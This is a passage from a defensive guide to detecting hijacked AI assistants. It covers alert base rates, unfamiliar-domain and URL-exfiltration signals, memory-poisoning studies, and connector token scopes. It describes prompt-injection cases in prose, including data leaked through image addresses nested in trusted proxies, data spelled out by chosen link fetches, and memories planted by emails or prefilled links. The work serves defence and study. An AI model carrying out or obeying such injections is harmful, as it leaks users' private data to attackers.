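Companies already use baselines to look for insiders, meaning staff who misuse their legitimate access. This is usually called user and entity behaviour analytics (UEBA), where an "entity" may be a device or a software account. An insider logs in with a real password and valid permissions, so the main evidence is often a change in habits.

A hijacked assistant also acts with valid permissions. Microsoft's *Configure agent-specific risk detection controls* tells administrators to add agents to insider-risk policies the same way they add users. But an employee planning to leave might change their behaviour over several weeks, while an injected instruction can redirect an assistant between one tool call and the next. *Agent Observability*, a page on a practitioners' wiki, also points out that many agents are short-lived. These agents may have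 no lasting identity to link a history to.

Two Salesforce security data scientists, Rittinghouse and Huang (2026), described how the company applies the method to Agentforce, a product its customers use to build their own agents. In their March 2026 conference talk, *1.8M Prompts, 30 Alerts*, they explained how their system reduces about 1.8 million prompts a day to fewer than 30 alerts. It uses records of what the agents did and doesn't read the prompts, which are customers' private data.

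According to a summary of the transcript, also titled *1.8M Prompts, 30 Alerts*, the system covers 55,000 customer organisations and more than 12,000 active agents a day. It scores each session against baselines for the user, the agent and the organisation, using measures such as the number of database calls, the share of the data that the session reads and how rarely agents use the fields it reads. Adding a baseline for each agent produced far fewer false alarms than user baselines alone, because an agent's logic is more constrained than a person's behaviour.

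Simple counts worked better than scoring the complexity of database queries. The team built the scoring tool because they expected thieves to use complex queries, but the agents write the queries themselves, so the score mostly reflected how a customer had designed its agent. The system compared sessions with the previous day's baselines in batches, so alerts arrived 12 to 24 hours late.

The summary calls 60,000 prompts per alert a signal-to-noise ratio, but the figure measures how much the system discards. Software that chose 30 prompts at random each day would achieve the same ratio. Judging the detector requires knowing how many alerts were real attacks and how many attacks it missed. The summary gives neither figure, and the team was still working on a way to record whether past alerts had been correct.

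### The base-rate argument

When attacks are rare, even an accurate detector produces mostly false alarms. Axelsson illustrates this with a medical test that is 99% accurate for both sick and healthy people, and a disease that affects one person in 10,000. Among a million people, the test flags 99 of the 100 who are sick, but also 9,999 who are healthy, so someone who tests positive has only about a 1% chance of having the disease. The base-rate fallacy is overlooking how rare the disease is.

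Axelsson applied the argument to a small computer network that produced a million log records a day. He assumed two intrusions a day, each affecting ten records, and treated every ten records as one event. If a detector caught every intrusion and raised a false alarm on one in 100,000 harmless events, two-thirds of its alerts would be real. If it raised a false alarm on one in 1,000, only about 2% of its alerts would be real. He concluded that the false alarm rate, rather than the ability to recognise attacks, limits a detector's usefulness.

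He assumed the attack frequency, but later evidence fits his argument. The survey *AI-Driven Security Alert Screening and Alert Fatigue Mitigation in Security Operations Centers* (2026) cites measurements from one large security operation where only about 0.01% of daily alerts related to true attacks.

The same calculation works for assistants. Let r be recall (the share of compromised sessions that the detector flags), f the false positive rate (the share of harmless sessions that it flags) and p the share of all sessions that are compromised. Precision, the share of alerts that are real, is then:

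$$\text{precision} = \frac{r \times p}{r \times p + f \times (1 - p)}$$

Suppose a company has 10,000 sessions a day, one of them compromised, and a detector with a recall of 0.67 and a false positive rate of 0.5%:

$$\frac{0.67 \times 0.0001}{0.67 \times 0.0001 + 0.005 \times 0.9999} \approx 0.013$$

Precision is about 1.3%. The company gets about 50 false alarms a day and a real alert on two days out of three. If each alert takes ten minutes to check, one person could spend the whole working day on them.

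The number of sessions and the recall are close to those Li and colleagues report for Uber's system, but the attack frequency and the false positive rate are assumptions. Uber's detector raised no false alarms on 260 harmless tasks, but its false positive rate could still be 0.5%, because a detector with that rate would raise none in more than a quarter of such tests.

Even catching every attack would raise precision to only about 2%. The detector would have to flag no more than about one in 15,000 harmless sessions for half of its alerts to be real.

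The false positive rate also has to be measured per session. The tasks in Uber's test averaged 28.5 tool calls. If a detector checked each call separately and wrongly flagged 0.5% of them, it would flag about 13% of harmless sessions of that length, assuming its errors were independent. The company would then have about 1,300 false alarms a day.

### Requiring two signals

A company can reduce false alarms by raising an alert only when two signals appear in the same session. Suppose each signal has the recall and false positive rate from the example. If the signals are independent, both appear in 0.67 × 0.67, or 45%, of compromised sessions, and in 0.005 × 0.005, or 0.0025%, of harmless ones. The company would get one false alarm every four days, and most alerts would be real, but it would miss more than half of the attacks.

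Two signals are independent here if a harmless session that triggers one is no more likely than any other harmless session to trigger the second. This is rarely true, because both signals can have the same cause. In Salesforce's example, Emma Martin's behaviour set off four alerts: too many rows, broader searches than usual, a burst of requests and a type of record she had never opened. The guide advises combining such alerts because they represent one change in behaviour. An honest employee who moved to a new project might also set off all four.

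The same problem affects the baselines for users, agents and organisations. According to the summary of the Salesforce talk, three correlated deviations are much less likely to occur by chance, but one large legitimate export could raise all three scores.

The last row of the table assumes that 20% of the harmless sessions that trigger one signal also trigger the other.

| Alert requires | Attacks found | False alarms | Precision |
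|---|---|---|---|
| One signal | 67% | 50 a day | 1.3% |
| Two independent signals | 45% | One every four days | 64% |
| Two signals with 20% overlap in false alarms | 45% | 10 a day | 4% |

A company can measure the overlap by checking how many of the harmless sessions that one signal flags also trigger the other. With 50 such sessions a day, it would have a reasonable estimate within a few weeks.

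Choosing signals with different causes should reduce the overlap. For example, a known attack phrase in a fetched page is largely unrelated to how many files the user normally opens. Some harmless sessions will still trigger both signals, particularly when a company hires people to imitate attackers. At Uber, such tests were the main source of the 17% of alerts that analysts labelled as real but not malicious.

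## Browsing to unfamiliar sites

Whoever sets up alerts for unfamiliar sites has to choose how much of the address to compare, whose browsing history to compare it with, and how far back that history should go. Comparing full addresses would make nearly every news article unfamiliar. Comparing domains can be too coarse, because thousands of unrelated people publish pages on github.io, each under their own subdomain. The period matters because a domain that nobody has opened for 30 days may have been popular last year.

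### Five definitions of "unfamiliar"

| Definition | Data it needs | Harmless pages it flags | Attacks it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| New to this user | The user's browsing history | Most pages in any new piece of research | Hostile comments on a site the user reads daily |
| New to the organisation | Every user's history | Specialist sources that only one person needs | Every victim after the first |
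| Recently registered | The domain's registration date | New companies, products and events | Old domains, and pages on large hosting services |
| Low reputation | Scores from a security company | Small sites with little history | Reputable sites that pass requests on |
| Not traceable to the user's request or a search result | The source of each address | Links followed from one page to another | Hostile sites that appear in search results |

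The last definition is the most useful for an assistant because it concerns how the assistant got the address. If Maya types a supplier's web address, it matters little that nobody in the company has opened it before. An address from a search result deserves less trust, since Tenable got its own hostile site into ChatGPT's results.

Some products enforce a version of this rule. According to Anthropic's documentation, *Web fetch tool*, the tool that lets Claude open pages accepts only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, so Claude can't compose a new address and open it.

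The same documentation warns about domains with lookalike letters, such as a Cyrillic "а" in what appears to be amazon.com. Software would correctly treat the domain as new, but a person reading the alert might dismiss it as a mistake. The log should also include the domain's plain ASCII form, which makes the difference visible.

### Why novelty is a weak signal

People ask an assistant to browse because it can find pages they don't already know. Suppose nine in ten compromised sessions involve a domain new to the organisation, and one in ten harmless sessions does too. If one session in 10,000 is compromised, fewer than one in 1,000 alerts triggered by new domains will be real.

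Elastic's *GenAI Process Connection to Unusual Domain* is a working alert of this type for Macs. It monitors connections by programs such as Claude, Cursor and Copilot and fires when a domain appears for the first time. Elastic exempts more than 100 domains and domain patterns to reduce the number of alerts, but still rates the rule's noise as medium. It lists harmless causes such as vendors changing their infrastructure and developers trying out new MCP servers.

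The exemptions cover everything under amazonaws.com, where anyone can rent a server. The rule also depends on connections from the user's own machine, so it can't detect pages that an assistant opens from its vendor's data centre.

Elastic uses some of the other definitions after the alert has fired, instructing the analyst to check whether the domain is recently registered or has a poor reputation, and whether other machines have contacted it. This seems sensible, because registration dates and reputation scores are more useful for sorting alerts than for generating them.

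### How an address carries data out

When a browser requests a page, the website receives the full address and commonly logs it, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains. An assistant that opens an address ending in an employee's name therefore gives that name to whoever runs the site, even if the page doesn't exist.

Search tools can leak data in the same way. PromptArmor's *The Risks of Connectors in Your AI Applications* points out that a "read-only" search still sends the query to another company. Link previews in chat apps can also leak data. Telegram and Slack show previews of links in messages, and PromptArmor found that generating a preview makes the same sort of request as a click. A link in an assistant's reply in one of these apps can therefore leak data immediately, and the assistant's own log may contain no page fetch.

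### Stronger signals

The following signals concern what an address contains and what happened before the request.

| Signal | Log fields it needs | Harmless behaviour that resembles it |
|---|---|---|
| Request to a new site soon after the assistant read private data | Order of entries, sensitivity of each result, destination | Looking up a company mentioned in an email |
| Long or random-looking text in the address | Full address, including everything after the domain | Signed download links, tracking codes, long searches |
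| Link taken from page content | Source of the address, and the author of that source | Following a link from a contents page to a report |
| Unexpected redirect | Every address in the chain | Shortened links, login pages, links in newsletters |
| Jump in fetches | Session identifier, type of task, time and address of each fetch | A research task, or paging through a catalogue |

The first signal is weak for an office assistant that reads email in nearly every session. It becomes much stronger if software finds part of the private text in the outgoing address. The software should also look for common encodings of that text, but it can't detect every way of disguising it.

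"Random-looking" can have an exact meaning. One common measure is Shannon entropy, the average information per character in bits, where $p_i$ is the share of the text that character $i$ makes up:

$$H = -\sum_i p_i \log_2 p_i$$

Ordinary English has an entropy of about 4 bits per character if one counts only letters, and encoded data often has more. But the measured entropy of a text of n characters can't exceed $\log_2 n$, so 16 characters of encoded data can score at most 4. An entropy test may therefore catch an encoded document but miss an encoded password.

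A rule that flags encoded text in web addresses would also flag many legitimate requests, since websites routinely put encoded text there. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (Zhang and Pei, 2026) describes an attack in which the leak looks like an ordinary search request with encoded text in one field. Limits on address length help a little. Anthropic's fetch tool rejects addresses over 250 characters, which prevents a long document from being sent in one request but leaves room for a name or a security code.

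#### A leak through ordinary links

An attacker can avoid long addresses by having the assistant choose among short ones. Willison (2026), a programmer who writes about language models, describes how Ayush Paul demonstrated this with Claude, whose fetch tool could open links found on pages it had already fetched. Paul's site offered a series of links, and the ones Claude followed spelled out the user's name, home city and employer.

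The evidence was a sequence of many fetches to one site, at addresses that differed by only a letter. No single address contained anything private. Paging through a catalogue produces a similar pattern, but the page numbers usually rise in order.

The number of fetches limits how much data such a leak can carry. If an assistant makes k fetches, each from a choice of N addresses, the sequence can carry at most this many bits:

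$$k \times \log_2 N$$

With 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, ten fetches can carry ten characters, or about 52 bits. With 1,000 addresses, two fetches are enough for a six-digit login code. An alert for unusually many fetches could catch the theft of a user's biography but would probably miss the theft of a login code.

Paul's site showed the hostile text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. An investigator who opened the page later in a normal browser would have found nothing suspicious, so the log has to keep the text the assistant received.

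### EchoLeak

EchoLeak was a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that let an outsider steal data by sending an email, without the recipient clicking anything. Aim Labs, a research group at a company that sold protection for AI systems, told Microsoft about it in January 2025. Microsoft finished fixing it in May, and Aim Labs published the details on 11 June, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Microsoft said the flaw had affected no customers, and the case study *EchoLeak* (2025) also reports no attacks outside the research.

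Ravia (2025) gives the first-hand account in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*. The hostile email read like instructions to its recipient and never mentioned AI, and Microsoft's injection detector missed it. When the user later asked Copilot about a related subject, such as hiring, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal material. Its reply included an image whose address contained sensitive information from the conversation.

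The user's browser tried to load the image automatically. Copilot's web page had a content security policy, a list of the domains from which the browser may load images. The list included Microsoft Teams but not the attacker's server. The image address pointed to a Teams service that fetches material from other sites, and the attacker's address was nested inside it. When the browser contacted Teams, the service contacted the attacker's server.

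Most of the signals would have been absent or weak:

- An alert for new domains would have missed the request, because office workers' browsers contact Teams all day.
- The request did follow a read of private data, but so do most of Copilot's answers.
- One image wouldn't have counted as a jump in fetches.
- The browser received no redirect, since Teams made the second request itself.
- The text in the address might have looked long or random, depending on what Copilot had put there.

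Tracing where the address came from could have worked better. Software that extracted the nested address would have found a domain unrelated to Microsoft, and could have traced that domain to an email from outside the company. An alert for that combination would have had a good chance of catching the leak. A search for exact copies of the full address would have failed, because Copilot had added the stolen text to it. The alert would also flag some legitimate replies, such as when a user asks to see a picture from a supplier's newsletter through an image-preview service.

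Few customers would have had the data for this check. As in HackedGPT, a log of tool calls would have missed the image request, and a web filter that recorded just domains would have shown only a connection to Teams. Ravia's team could also get Copilot to leave the hostile email out of its citations. Korman found that summer that Copilot's audit log could fail to record files that weren't linked in the reply, so the log might have omitted the email too.

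### Trusted domains that forward traffic

A list of trusted domains is useful only if data sent to those domains stays with their owners. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, as the bing.com links in HackedGPT did. Software can handle redirects by checking each new address before following it. This check doesn't work when the trusted site fetches the outside address itself, as Teams did in EchoLeak, because the second request doesn't go through the user's browser.

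A year after EchoLeak, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) reported the same weakness in Copilot. The attack began when a user clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address. Copilot searched the user's mailbox and put the title of an email into an image address at Bing, which was on the list of permitted domains. Bing's image search then fetched the attacker's address. Microsoft has since fixed the flaw.

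SearchLeak also shows why a log of final replies isn't enough. Microsoft's software converted dangerous parts of a reply into harmless text only after Copilot had finished writing, and by then the browser had already loaded the image. An investigator reading the finished reply might conclude that the protection had worked, but the browser's request log would show that the data had left.

Trusted domains can also change owners. The Hacker News (2025) reported in September on ForcedLeak, a flaw in Salesforce's Agentforce that involved an expired domain on its trusted list. Anyone could have registered the domain and received whatever the assistant sent there. Salesforce took back the domain and began blocking output to addresses outside its trusted list. Checking registration dates might have caught a new owner, so such checks are worth running even on trusted domains.

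Varonis recommends reviewing every permitted domain for services that fetch URLs supplied by users. This is worthwhile but laborious for the domains of a large company like Microsoft, which runs thousands of services and can add one at any time. A customer could reduce the work by permitting only the exact hosts and paths that its assistant needs.

OpenAI instead checks the whole address against an index of public web addresses, collected by a crawler with no access to users' conversations. ChatGPT can automatically open an address that is in the index, because an address that existed independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's data. An address with a newly inserted secret, like the one in EchoLeak, would almost certainly not be in the index.

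OpenAI's check is weaker against leaks that encode data in the choice of which existing pages to request. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* notes that any large blog probably has enough indexed pages to represent every letter and digit. It suggests preventing an assistant from requesting the same address twice in a session. That would make it harder to spell words with repeated letters, though some data could still get out. Even so, the post calls the check a significant improvement, and adds that OpenAI's developers have to remember to use it in every product.

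### Opaque code and encoded text

AI News also recommends an alert for attempts to summarise opaque code blocks. These contain text that a person can't readily understand, such as compressed program code or a file encoded as letters and digits. Attackers can use them to hide instructions from a human reviewer or a filter that searches for known phrases, but an assistant may be able to decode the instructions and follow them.

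Encoded or obscure text is common in legitimate work, and hostile requests are probably a tiny share of the total. Developers ask about obscure code, and support staff paste in encoded error messages. Even a request to read a PDF can produce encoded text, because Anthropic's fetch tool returns PDFs as base64, a common way of writing a file as plain characters. An alert on all encoded text would therefore fire whenever Claude used this tool to open a PDF.

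The alert would be more useful if it also required that the address appeared only in text the assistant had decoded. For example, a user might ask what an encoded passage means, and the assistant might decode it and then contact an address found only in the result. The user asked for an explanation, so the request to that address needs a reason. To detect this, the log must hold the original text, the decoded text and the source of the address. A developer who asks the assistant to test a decoded script could still trigger the alert.

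Varonis suggests another narrow check for links that open Copilot with a prefilled prompt, which is to look for prompts that contain HTML tags or instructions to put data into image addresses. Employees rarely type either when searching their own mailbox, so this should produce far fewer false alarms than an alert for long or encoded text.

### Holding the request or restricting access

A single request can be enough to leak data, so software has to act on the strongest signals before the request is sent. When OpenAI's system can't verify an address, it either prompts the assistant to try another site or shows the user a warning. OpenAI applies a related check to searches and page visits in Deep Research, where a user may not be watching.

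OpenAI observes that frequent false alarms can teach people to click through warnings. A warning is also of little use if it shows only a familiar domain, as it would have in EchoLeak. It should show the final destination and, where possible, the private text that would go there.

If an assistant has a narrow job, the company can block every site the job doesn't require. *Building Browser Agents* (2025) gives the example of an agent that copies customer records into Salesforce and needs access to only two domains. Code outside the model enforces the limit, as David C advises. The allowed domains still need the checks for forwarding described above.

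General assistants need limits that depend on the task. *Environment Steering* (2026) proposes that an assistant whose task names a web address may visit only that address. If the task names no address, browsing is unrestricted, so this rule does not protect open-ended research.

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a more flexible approach in Google's Chrome browser. A separate model checks whether a new site is relevant to the user's task before the assistant visits it. That model doesn't receive the text of web pages, so instructions on a hostile page can't reach it directly. Chrome also restricts web addresses written by the assistant's model to known public ones. The full design distinguishes between sites the assistant may only read and sites where it may also click and type, but the first version tracked only the second group.

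Anthropic responded to Paul's demonstration by stopping Claude's fetch tool from following links it finds on fetched pages. This blocks the method he used, but it also prevents Claude from opening a report listed on a contents page unless the user supplies the link or a search returns it.

A company could apply that restriction only after a session has read both private data and text from an outsider. The software would then hold every request to a new site until the user approves it. Ordinary research could continue without interruption in a separate session that has no access to the user's files or memories. If a suspicious request has already gone out, staff can use the full address in the log to work out what data it sent. Elastic also advises replacing any passwords or keys the assistant was using.

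## Bursts of memory writes

If an assistant saves something to memory from a web page it opens once, that page can affect its answers months later. AI News therefore recommends an alert for unusual bursts of memory writes. The alert is useful only if attacks usually produce such bursts and harmless sessions rarely do.

### How assistants write and read memories

Dash, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory*, describe four ways in which an agent comes to write a memory:

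- It obeys an explicit instruction, such as "remember that I'm vegetarian".
- It follows a standing instruction from its developer to save anything useful.
- Its software summarises a long session to make room for more text.
- It turns a finished task into a procedure for next time.

Only the first needs a request, and requests are rare. *The Algorithmic Self-Portrait* (Dash, Wu and colleagues, 2026) examined 2,050 memories in ChatGPT histories that users had donated, and found that the user had asked for 4% of them. *Vulnerabilities in Personalization* (Zaman and Hoque, 2026) found that users had asked for just under 5% of 7,051 memories. Both teams identified requests by searching for words such as "remember", so they may have missed some indirect ones, but probably not enough to change the conclusion.

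A count of memory writes per session would miss those that some software makes outside the session. Mem0, an open-source system, uses a separate model to extract facts from conversations. OpenAI's *Dreaming* describes a background process that builds ChatGPT's memory from many past chats. OpenAI began rolling out a much-expanded version of this process in June 2026.

Assistants also differ in how they read memories. Some load them all at the start of a session, some automatically retrieve those most similar to the user's message, and others search only when the model calls a memory tool. Dash, Ge and colleagues planted memories in two agents. In HERMES, which loads memories automatically, 65% of the successfully planted memories affected a later session. In OpenClaw, which has to search for them, 17% did. Automatic loading involves no tool call, so a log of tool calls would not show which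 memories the model received.

A planted memory can remain after the attacker takes down the source page or the user deletes the chat, because the assistant keeps its own copy. According to OpenAI's *Memory in ChatGPT*, deleting a chat does not automatically delete a memory saved from it.

In *Trojan Hippo*, Piet, Das and colleagues (2026) tested how long a planted memory stays effective. A simulated email assistant read one hostile email, went through 100 harmless sessions and then received a question about a private matter, such as the user's taxes. Running on Gemini 3.1 Pro with no defences, it sent the user's details to the attacker in 80 to 100% of cases, depending on the type of memory. Each figure comes from only about 20 cases, and the researchers had refined the emails against the same kind of assistant, which most attackers would have less opportunity to do. When the researchers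 reused emails refined on GPT-5-mini against the larger GPT-5, the success rate ranged from zero to 70%, depending on the type of memory.

### The likeness to stored cross-site scripting

Websites have a similar problem called stored cross-site scripting. An attacker posts a comment containing code, the website saves it, and the code runs in the browser of everyone who later views the comment. As with a planted memory, the harm comes after the attacker has left, and an investigator has to look for an earlier write to explain it.

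Developers can prevent this attack by encoding comments so that browsers display any code as ordinary text. Memories have no equivalent fix, because their purpose is to influence the model. A memory such as "the user prefers short answers" would be useless if it couldn't affect replies.

A planted memory can also be harder to find than a hostile comment on a website. The website usually stores the comment as the attacker wrote it, so the operator can search for exact copies, but an assistant may reword a memory or merge it with others. A hostile comment can affect thousands of visitors, any of whom might report it, while a personal memory usually affects one user, who has nobody to compare answers with.

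The attacker has less control than with a website, because a browser follows the code exactly, while a model may never retrieve the planted memory or may retrieve it and not act on it.

### From demonstrations to marketing

Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported to OpenAI in May 2024 that a web page could plant false memories in ChatGPT. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security concern. A month later he sent a demonstration in which a planted memory made ChatGPT's Mac app leak every later message and reply. His post *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* says OpenAI fixed the leak in September, but that web pages could still write memories. HackedGPT's memory attack relied on the same weakness a year later.

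Google had tried to prevent such writes by generally stopping Gemini from using sensitive tools while it was processing untrusted material. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Gemini's Memory with Prompt Injection and Delayed Tool Invocation* describes a test in which Gemini wrote to memory one turn later. The session's log would contain a document, a summary, a one-word reply from the user and then a memory containing facts the user had never mentioned. Gemini displayed a notice when it saved the memory. Google rated both the likelihood and the impact of the attack as low.

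Radware's *ZombieAgent* reports a planted memory that made ChatGPT carry out the attacker's task before answering any question. The attack should be easier to detect when the assistant reads the memory than when it writes it, because the same unrequested action would recur across sessions.

Companies have since tried to plant memories as marketing. Microsoft (2026) examined links to AI assistants in email traffic over 60 days and found 50 different prompts intended to plant a recommendation in an assistant's memory. They came from 31 real businesses in 14 industries, including health and finance, and one of the businesses sold security products. Many of the prompts were behind "Summarize with AI" buttons, which opened an assistant with a prefilled request to summarise a page and remember the company as a trusted source.

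These figures count attempts, not memories that an assistant saved. Microsoft says success varied between assistants and over time, and that it could no longer reproduce several behaviours others had reported. But a successful attempt would be hard to notice, because the assistant might recommend a particular supplier without sending any data, opening an unfamiliar site or breaking a rule.

Newer models do not necessarily resist planted memories. *Hidden in Memory* (Pulipaka, Hlebik et al., 2026) put hostile text into documents such as news articles, legal filings and code. Assistants running on GPT-5.5 saved the planted memory in up to 99.8% of tests. Claude Sonnet 4.6 saved only 15 of the 200 memories meant to influence an assistant's later actions. A change of model could therefore greatly increase or reduce a company's risk, which is another reason to log the model version with each write.

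### How often harmless sessions produce a burst

Suppose that sessions average 0.4 memory writes and that each write is independent of the others. The number of writes in a session then follows a Poisson distribution, the standard model for independent events that occur at a steady average rate. The probability of five or more is:

$$P(X \geq 5) = 1 - \sum_{k=0}^{4} \frac{e^{-0.4} \, 0.4^k}{k!} \approx 0.00006$$

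That is about 6 sessions in 100,000. A company with 10,000 sessions a day would get 0.6 false alarms a day, which one person could easily check.

Real writes are not independent, however. A new user may tell the assistant their name, job, diet and preferred writing style within a few minutes, and the assistant may save each as a separate memory. In the data from Dash, Wu and colleagues, conversations with at least one memory write averaged 1.9 writes. If writes were independent and averaged 0.4 per conversation overall, that figure would be 1.2. The true overall average may be well below 0.4, since Zaman and Hoque's data gives about 0.04 memories per conversation. At that rate, if writes were independent, nearly every conversation with a write would have exactly one.

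Clustering greatly increases the number of false alarms. Suppose one session in 100 is a set-up session with an average of six writes, and the others have slightly fewer than before, so the overall average is still 0.4. About 71% of the set-up sessions would have five or more writes. The company would then get about 72 false alarms a day instead of 0.6.

Raising the threshold to 13 writes would bring alerts back below one a day, but an attacker could then make 12 writes without triggering one. The company could instead exempt new users, who account for many of the bursts, although their memories need protection too.

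### One write is enough

The bigger problem with a burst alarm is that an attacker doesn't need a burst. HackedGPT's memory attack, Rehberger's spyware and the email in *Trojan Hippo* could each work through a single saved entry, so the alarm would miss all three even if the company solved the problem of false alarms.

A burst alarm could still catch a clumsy attack, or a fault that makes an assistant save the same fact repeatedly. It might also catch an attacker who plants many versions of a memory to make retrieval more likely. The alarm takes few resources to run, but a company shouldn't rely on it to detect planted memories.

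### Checking where a memory came from

Other checks look at the content and origin of each write. At 0.4 writes per session, the company in the example has 4,000 writes a day, so a check that wrongly flags 1% of them produces 40 false alarms a day.

| Check | What the log needs | What it could miss |
|---|---|---|
| Memory written after the assistant read outside text | Order of entries, and who wrote each page, email or file | Writes by a background process with no record of its sources |
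| Memory phrased as an instruction | Full text of the memory | False statements that look like ordinary facts |
| Memory with no basis in the user's own words | The user's messages, kept apart from fetched text | A planted memory that resembles something the user said |
| User's approval | The text shown to the user, and the answer | Memories that the user approves without reading |

#### Writes after outside text

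Piet and colleagues tested a strict version of the first check, in which their assistant could write no more memories in a session once it had opened the inbox. This reduced the attack's success rate to between 0 and 5%. The rule would also apply to a delayed write later in the session, like the one in Rehberger's Gemini test.

Blocking memory writes also kept the assistant from remembering anything useful from an email, such as a new contact's details. With one type of memory, Gemini's average success on ordinary tasks fell from 99% to 71%. A company could raise an alert instead of blocking the write, but an office assistant that reads email in most sessions would trigger an alert for most of its memories.

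#### Text phrased as an instruction

Dash, Ge and colleagues contrast two planted memories. One tells the assistant to remember that the user prefers to skip a login check. The other says that staff routinely re-enter their Wi-Fi passwords at a particular address. The second contains no command to the assistant, so a detector that looks for instructions has little to detect.

The best of the four detectors tested caught 84% of attacks with obvious signs, such as explicit commands, but only 42.5% of those that resembled ordinary information. It flagged 1% of harmless inputs. After it was adapted to memory attacks, its overall detection rate fell from 68% to 62%.

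Many legitimate memories are also instructions, such as Microsoft's example "always respond formally". For the marketing links, Microsoft recommends searching email and chat messages for links to assistants whose prefilled prompts contain words such as "remember" or "trusted source". That search is much narrower because few people put such a request in a link. It can show that a user clicked, but not that the assistant saved anything.

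#### Memories the user's words don't support

Software can also compare a new memory with what the user has said. Dash, Wu and colleagues used GPT-4o to compare ordinary ChatGPT memories with each user's full history. It classified 5% of the memories as weakly supported and 4% as unsupported. A company that flagged both groups would get about 360 alerts a day.

Some of these memories came from uploaded files, which GPT-4o did not receive. For example, one user uploaded a file and asked for a cover letter, and ChatGPT saved the user's name. In a log, this would look much like an attack, because in both cases the assistant reads a document and saves a fact that the user never typed.

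This check would be more useful combined with the first. An alert could require that the assistant had read outside text, that the memory resembled that text and that the user had said nothing similar. The company would have to test how many harmless writes in its own logs still met all three conditions.

#### Asking the user

Rehberger recommends that assistants ask for confirmation before saving a memory. A notice afterwards is weaker, and Zaman and Hoque found in their tests that ChatGPT's "Memory updated" notice did not always appear. But asking about all 4,000 writes a day would soon lead people to approve them automatically. The assistant could ask only about memories that the combined check flags.

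When the assistant asks the user to approve a memory write, the question should show the exact text and where it came from. "Save this preference?" is easy to approve, but a user who sees that the preference came from a supplier's website has a reason to refuse. The log should record both the question and the answer, because in the Gemini test the user said yes to something else.

#### Using the source when the assistant reads

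Once the log records each memory's source, software can also use that source to limit the memory's influence. *Utility Under Attack* (2026) reports a failed attempt to do this by ranking untrusted memories lower in search results. The penalty could offset an advantage of at most 0.175 in similarity to the user's question. False memories phrased like the question gained 0.32, so they still ranked first.

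A fixed rule works better against theft. In their strictest defence, Piet and colleagues labelled every memory written after the assistant had opened the inbox, and blocked outgoing email in any session that loaded a labelled memory. No attack succeeded, but the rule also blocked email once the assistant had read the inbox in the current session, so the assistant could not read a message and reply to it. A company could relax the rule by asking the user to approve the recipient.

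### Rolling back a planted memory

Rolling back means returning the memory to its state before the attack. Clearing the whole memory, as AI News recommends, is simpler, but the user loses years of useful entries.

*memorywire* (2026), which proposes a common format for memory operations, scores recovery in a way that penalises both leaving the attack in place and deleting too much:

$$\text{score} = \frac{2EU}{E + U} \times R$$

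E measures how completely the planted memories are gone, U how much useful memory remains, and R how well the memory store resists their return. Doing nothing and deleting everything both score zero. In a test with 30 planted memories, recovery using detectors of suspicious content scored only 0.036. Records of each memory's source helped recovery most, though the team that created the record format also designed the test.

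Deleting a planted memory may not remove its influence. Suppose Maya's assistant saves a supplier's claim that Norwood is her firm's approved supplier. A background process later combines this with other memories into "Maya buys office equipment, mainly from Norwood". If staff delete only the first entry, the second will still lead the assistant to favour Norwood. *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) says a rollback should include summaries and anything else that came from the planted memory. It also recommends quarantining the entries before deleting them, because deletion can destroy the evidence of what happened.

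Besides the old and new text of each memory, the log needs these fields:

| Field | Use in a rollback |
|---|---|
| Memory identifier and version | Finds the entry after later edits |
| Who or what made the change | Separates the user's edits from those of the model or a background process |
| Source page, email or file | Finds other memories from the same source |
| Earlier memories used to write this one | Finds summaries that absorbed the planted text |
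| Sessions that loaded the memory | Identifies answers and actions to review |
| Times of quarantine, deletion and restoration | Shows when the memory could still affect the assistant |

Existing products may record only some of these. *SuperLocalMemory* (2026) describes a system that records which agent wrote each memory, the protocol it used, a trust score and a history of changes. This would let staff isolate everything one agent wrote, but those four fields do not identify the web page or email a memory came from.

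Staff also need to check that the rollback worked. *MemSecBench* (2026), a test of memory attacks and repairs, compares copies of the memory store from before and after a repair, rather than treating a delete command or the agent's own report as proof. A repair succeeds only if the planted meaning is gone, including any reworded version, and the useful memories remain.

With ChatGPT, a planted memory could also return from the chat that produced it. OpenAI advises users to delete the saved memory, the original chat and any other source that contains the information. Selecting "Don't mention this again" deletes none of these. If the user turns memory off and later back on, ChatGPT may create new memories from the remaining chats.

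An investigator should therefore save a copy of the chat before deleting it. OpenAI offers a version history for saved memories on some plans, and says it may keep logs of deleted memories for up to 30 days. In *Trojan Hippo*, the planted memory still worked after 100 sessions, which is more than a month for someone who uses an assistant three times a day.

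## Connector access outside policy

The last alert on AI News' list is for connector access outside policy boundaries. A company without such a policy has only the permissions someone granted when setting up the connector, and these usually cover far more than the assistant's job requires.

### How a user authorises a connector

Connectors commonly use OAuth, a standard that lets one application act in another on a user's behalf without learning the user's password. When Maya connects her mailbox, her mail provider shows her the permissions, called scopes, that the assistant's software has requested. One scope might cover reading mail and another sending it. If she agrees, the provider issues a delegated token, a string of characters that the software sends with each request. Agarwal, writing for the vendor Averlon, explains that the provider ties the token to one application, which stores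 it on its own servers.

The software usually receives two tokens. The access token expires quickly, often after about an hour, and the refresh token lets the software get new access tokens without asking Maya again. BeyondTrust's *How Command Injection Vulnerability in OpenAI Codex Leads to GitHub Token Compromise* describes the access tokens of Codex's GitHub connector as short-lived, while Help Net Security's *The modern attack chain* (2026) warns that stolen tokens don't expire and survive password resets. Both can be right, because a thief who has the refresh token, and any secret the application uses to identify itself, can keep renewing the access token.

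Most services accept a token from whoever presents it, so a thief can call the mailbox directly without going near the assistant.

### Why scopes are broader than the task

Maya grants the scopes before anyone knows what she will ask for, so they have to cover every task she might request. Scopes also describe types of action rather than purposes. A scope can allow an assistant to send mail, but it typically can't limit the mail to people Maya has named. In her session, the assistant leaked the supplier prices using a permission she had given it.

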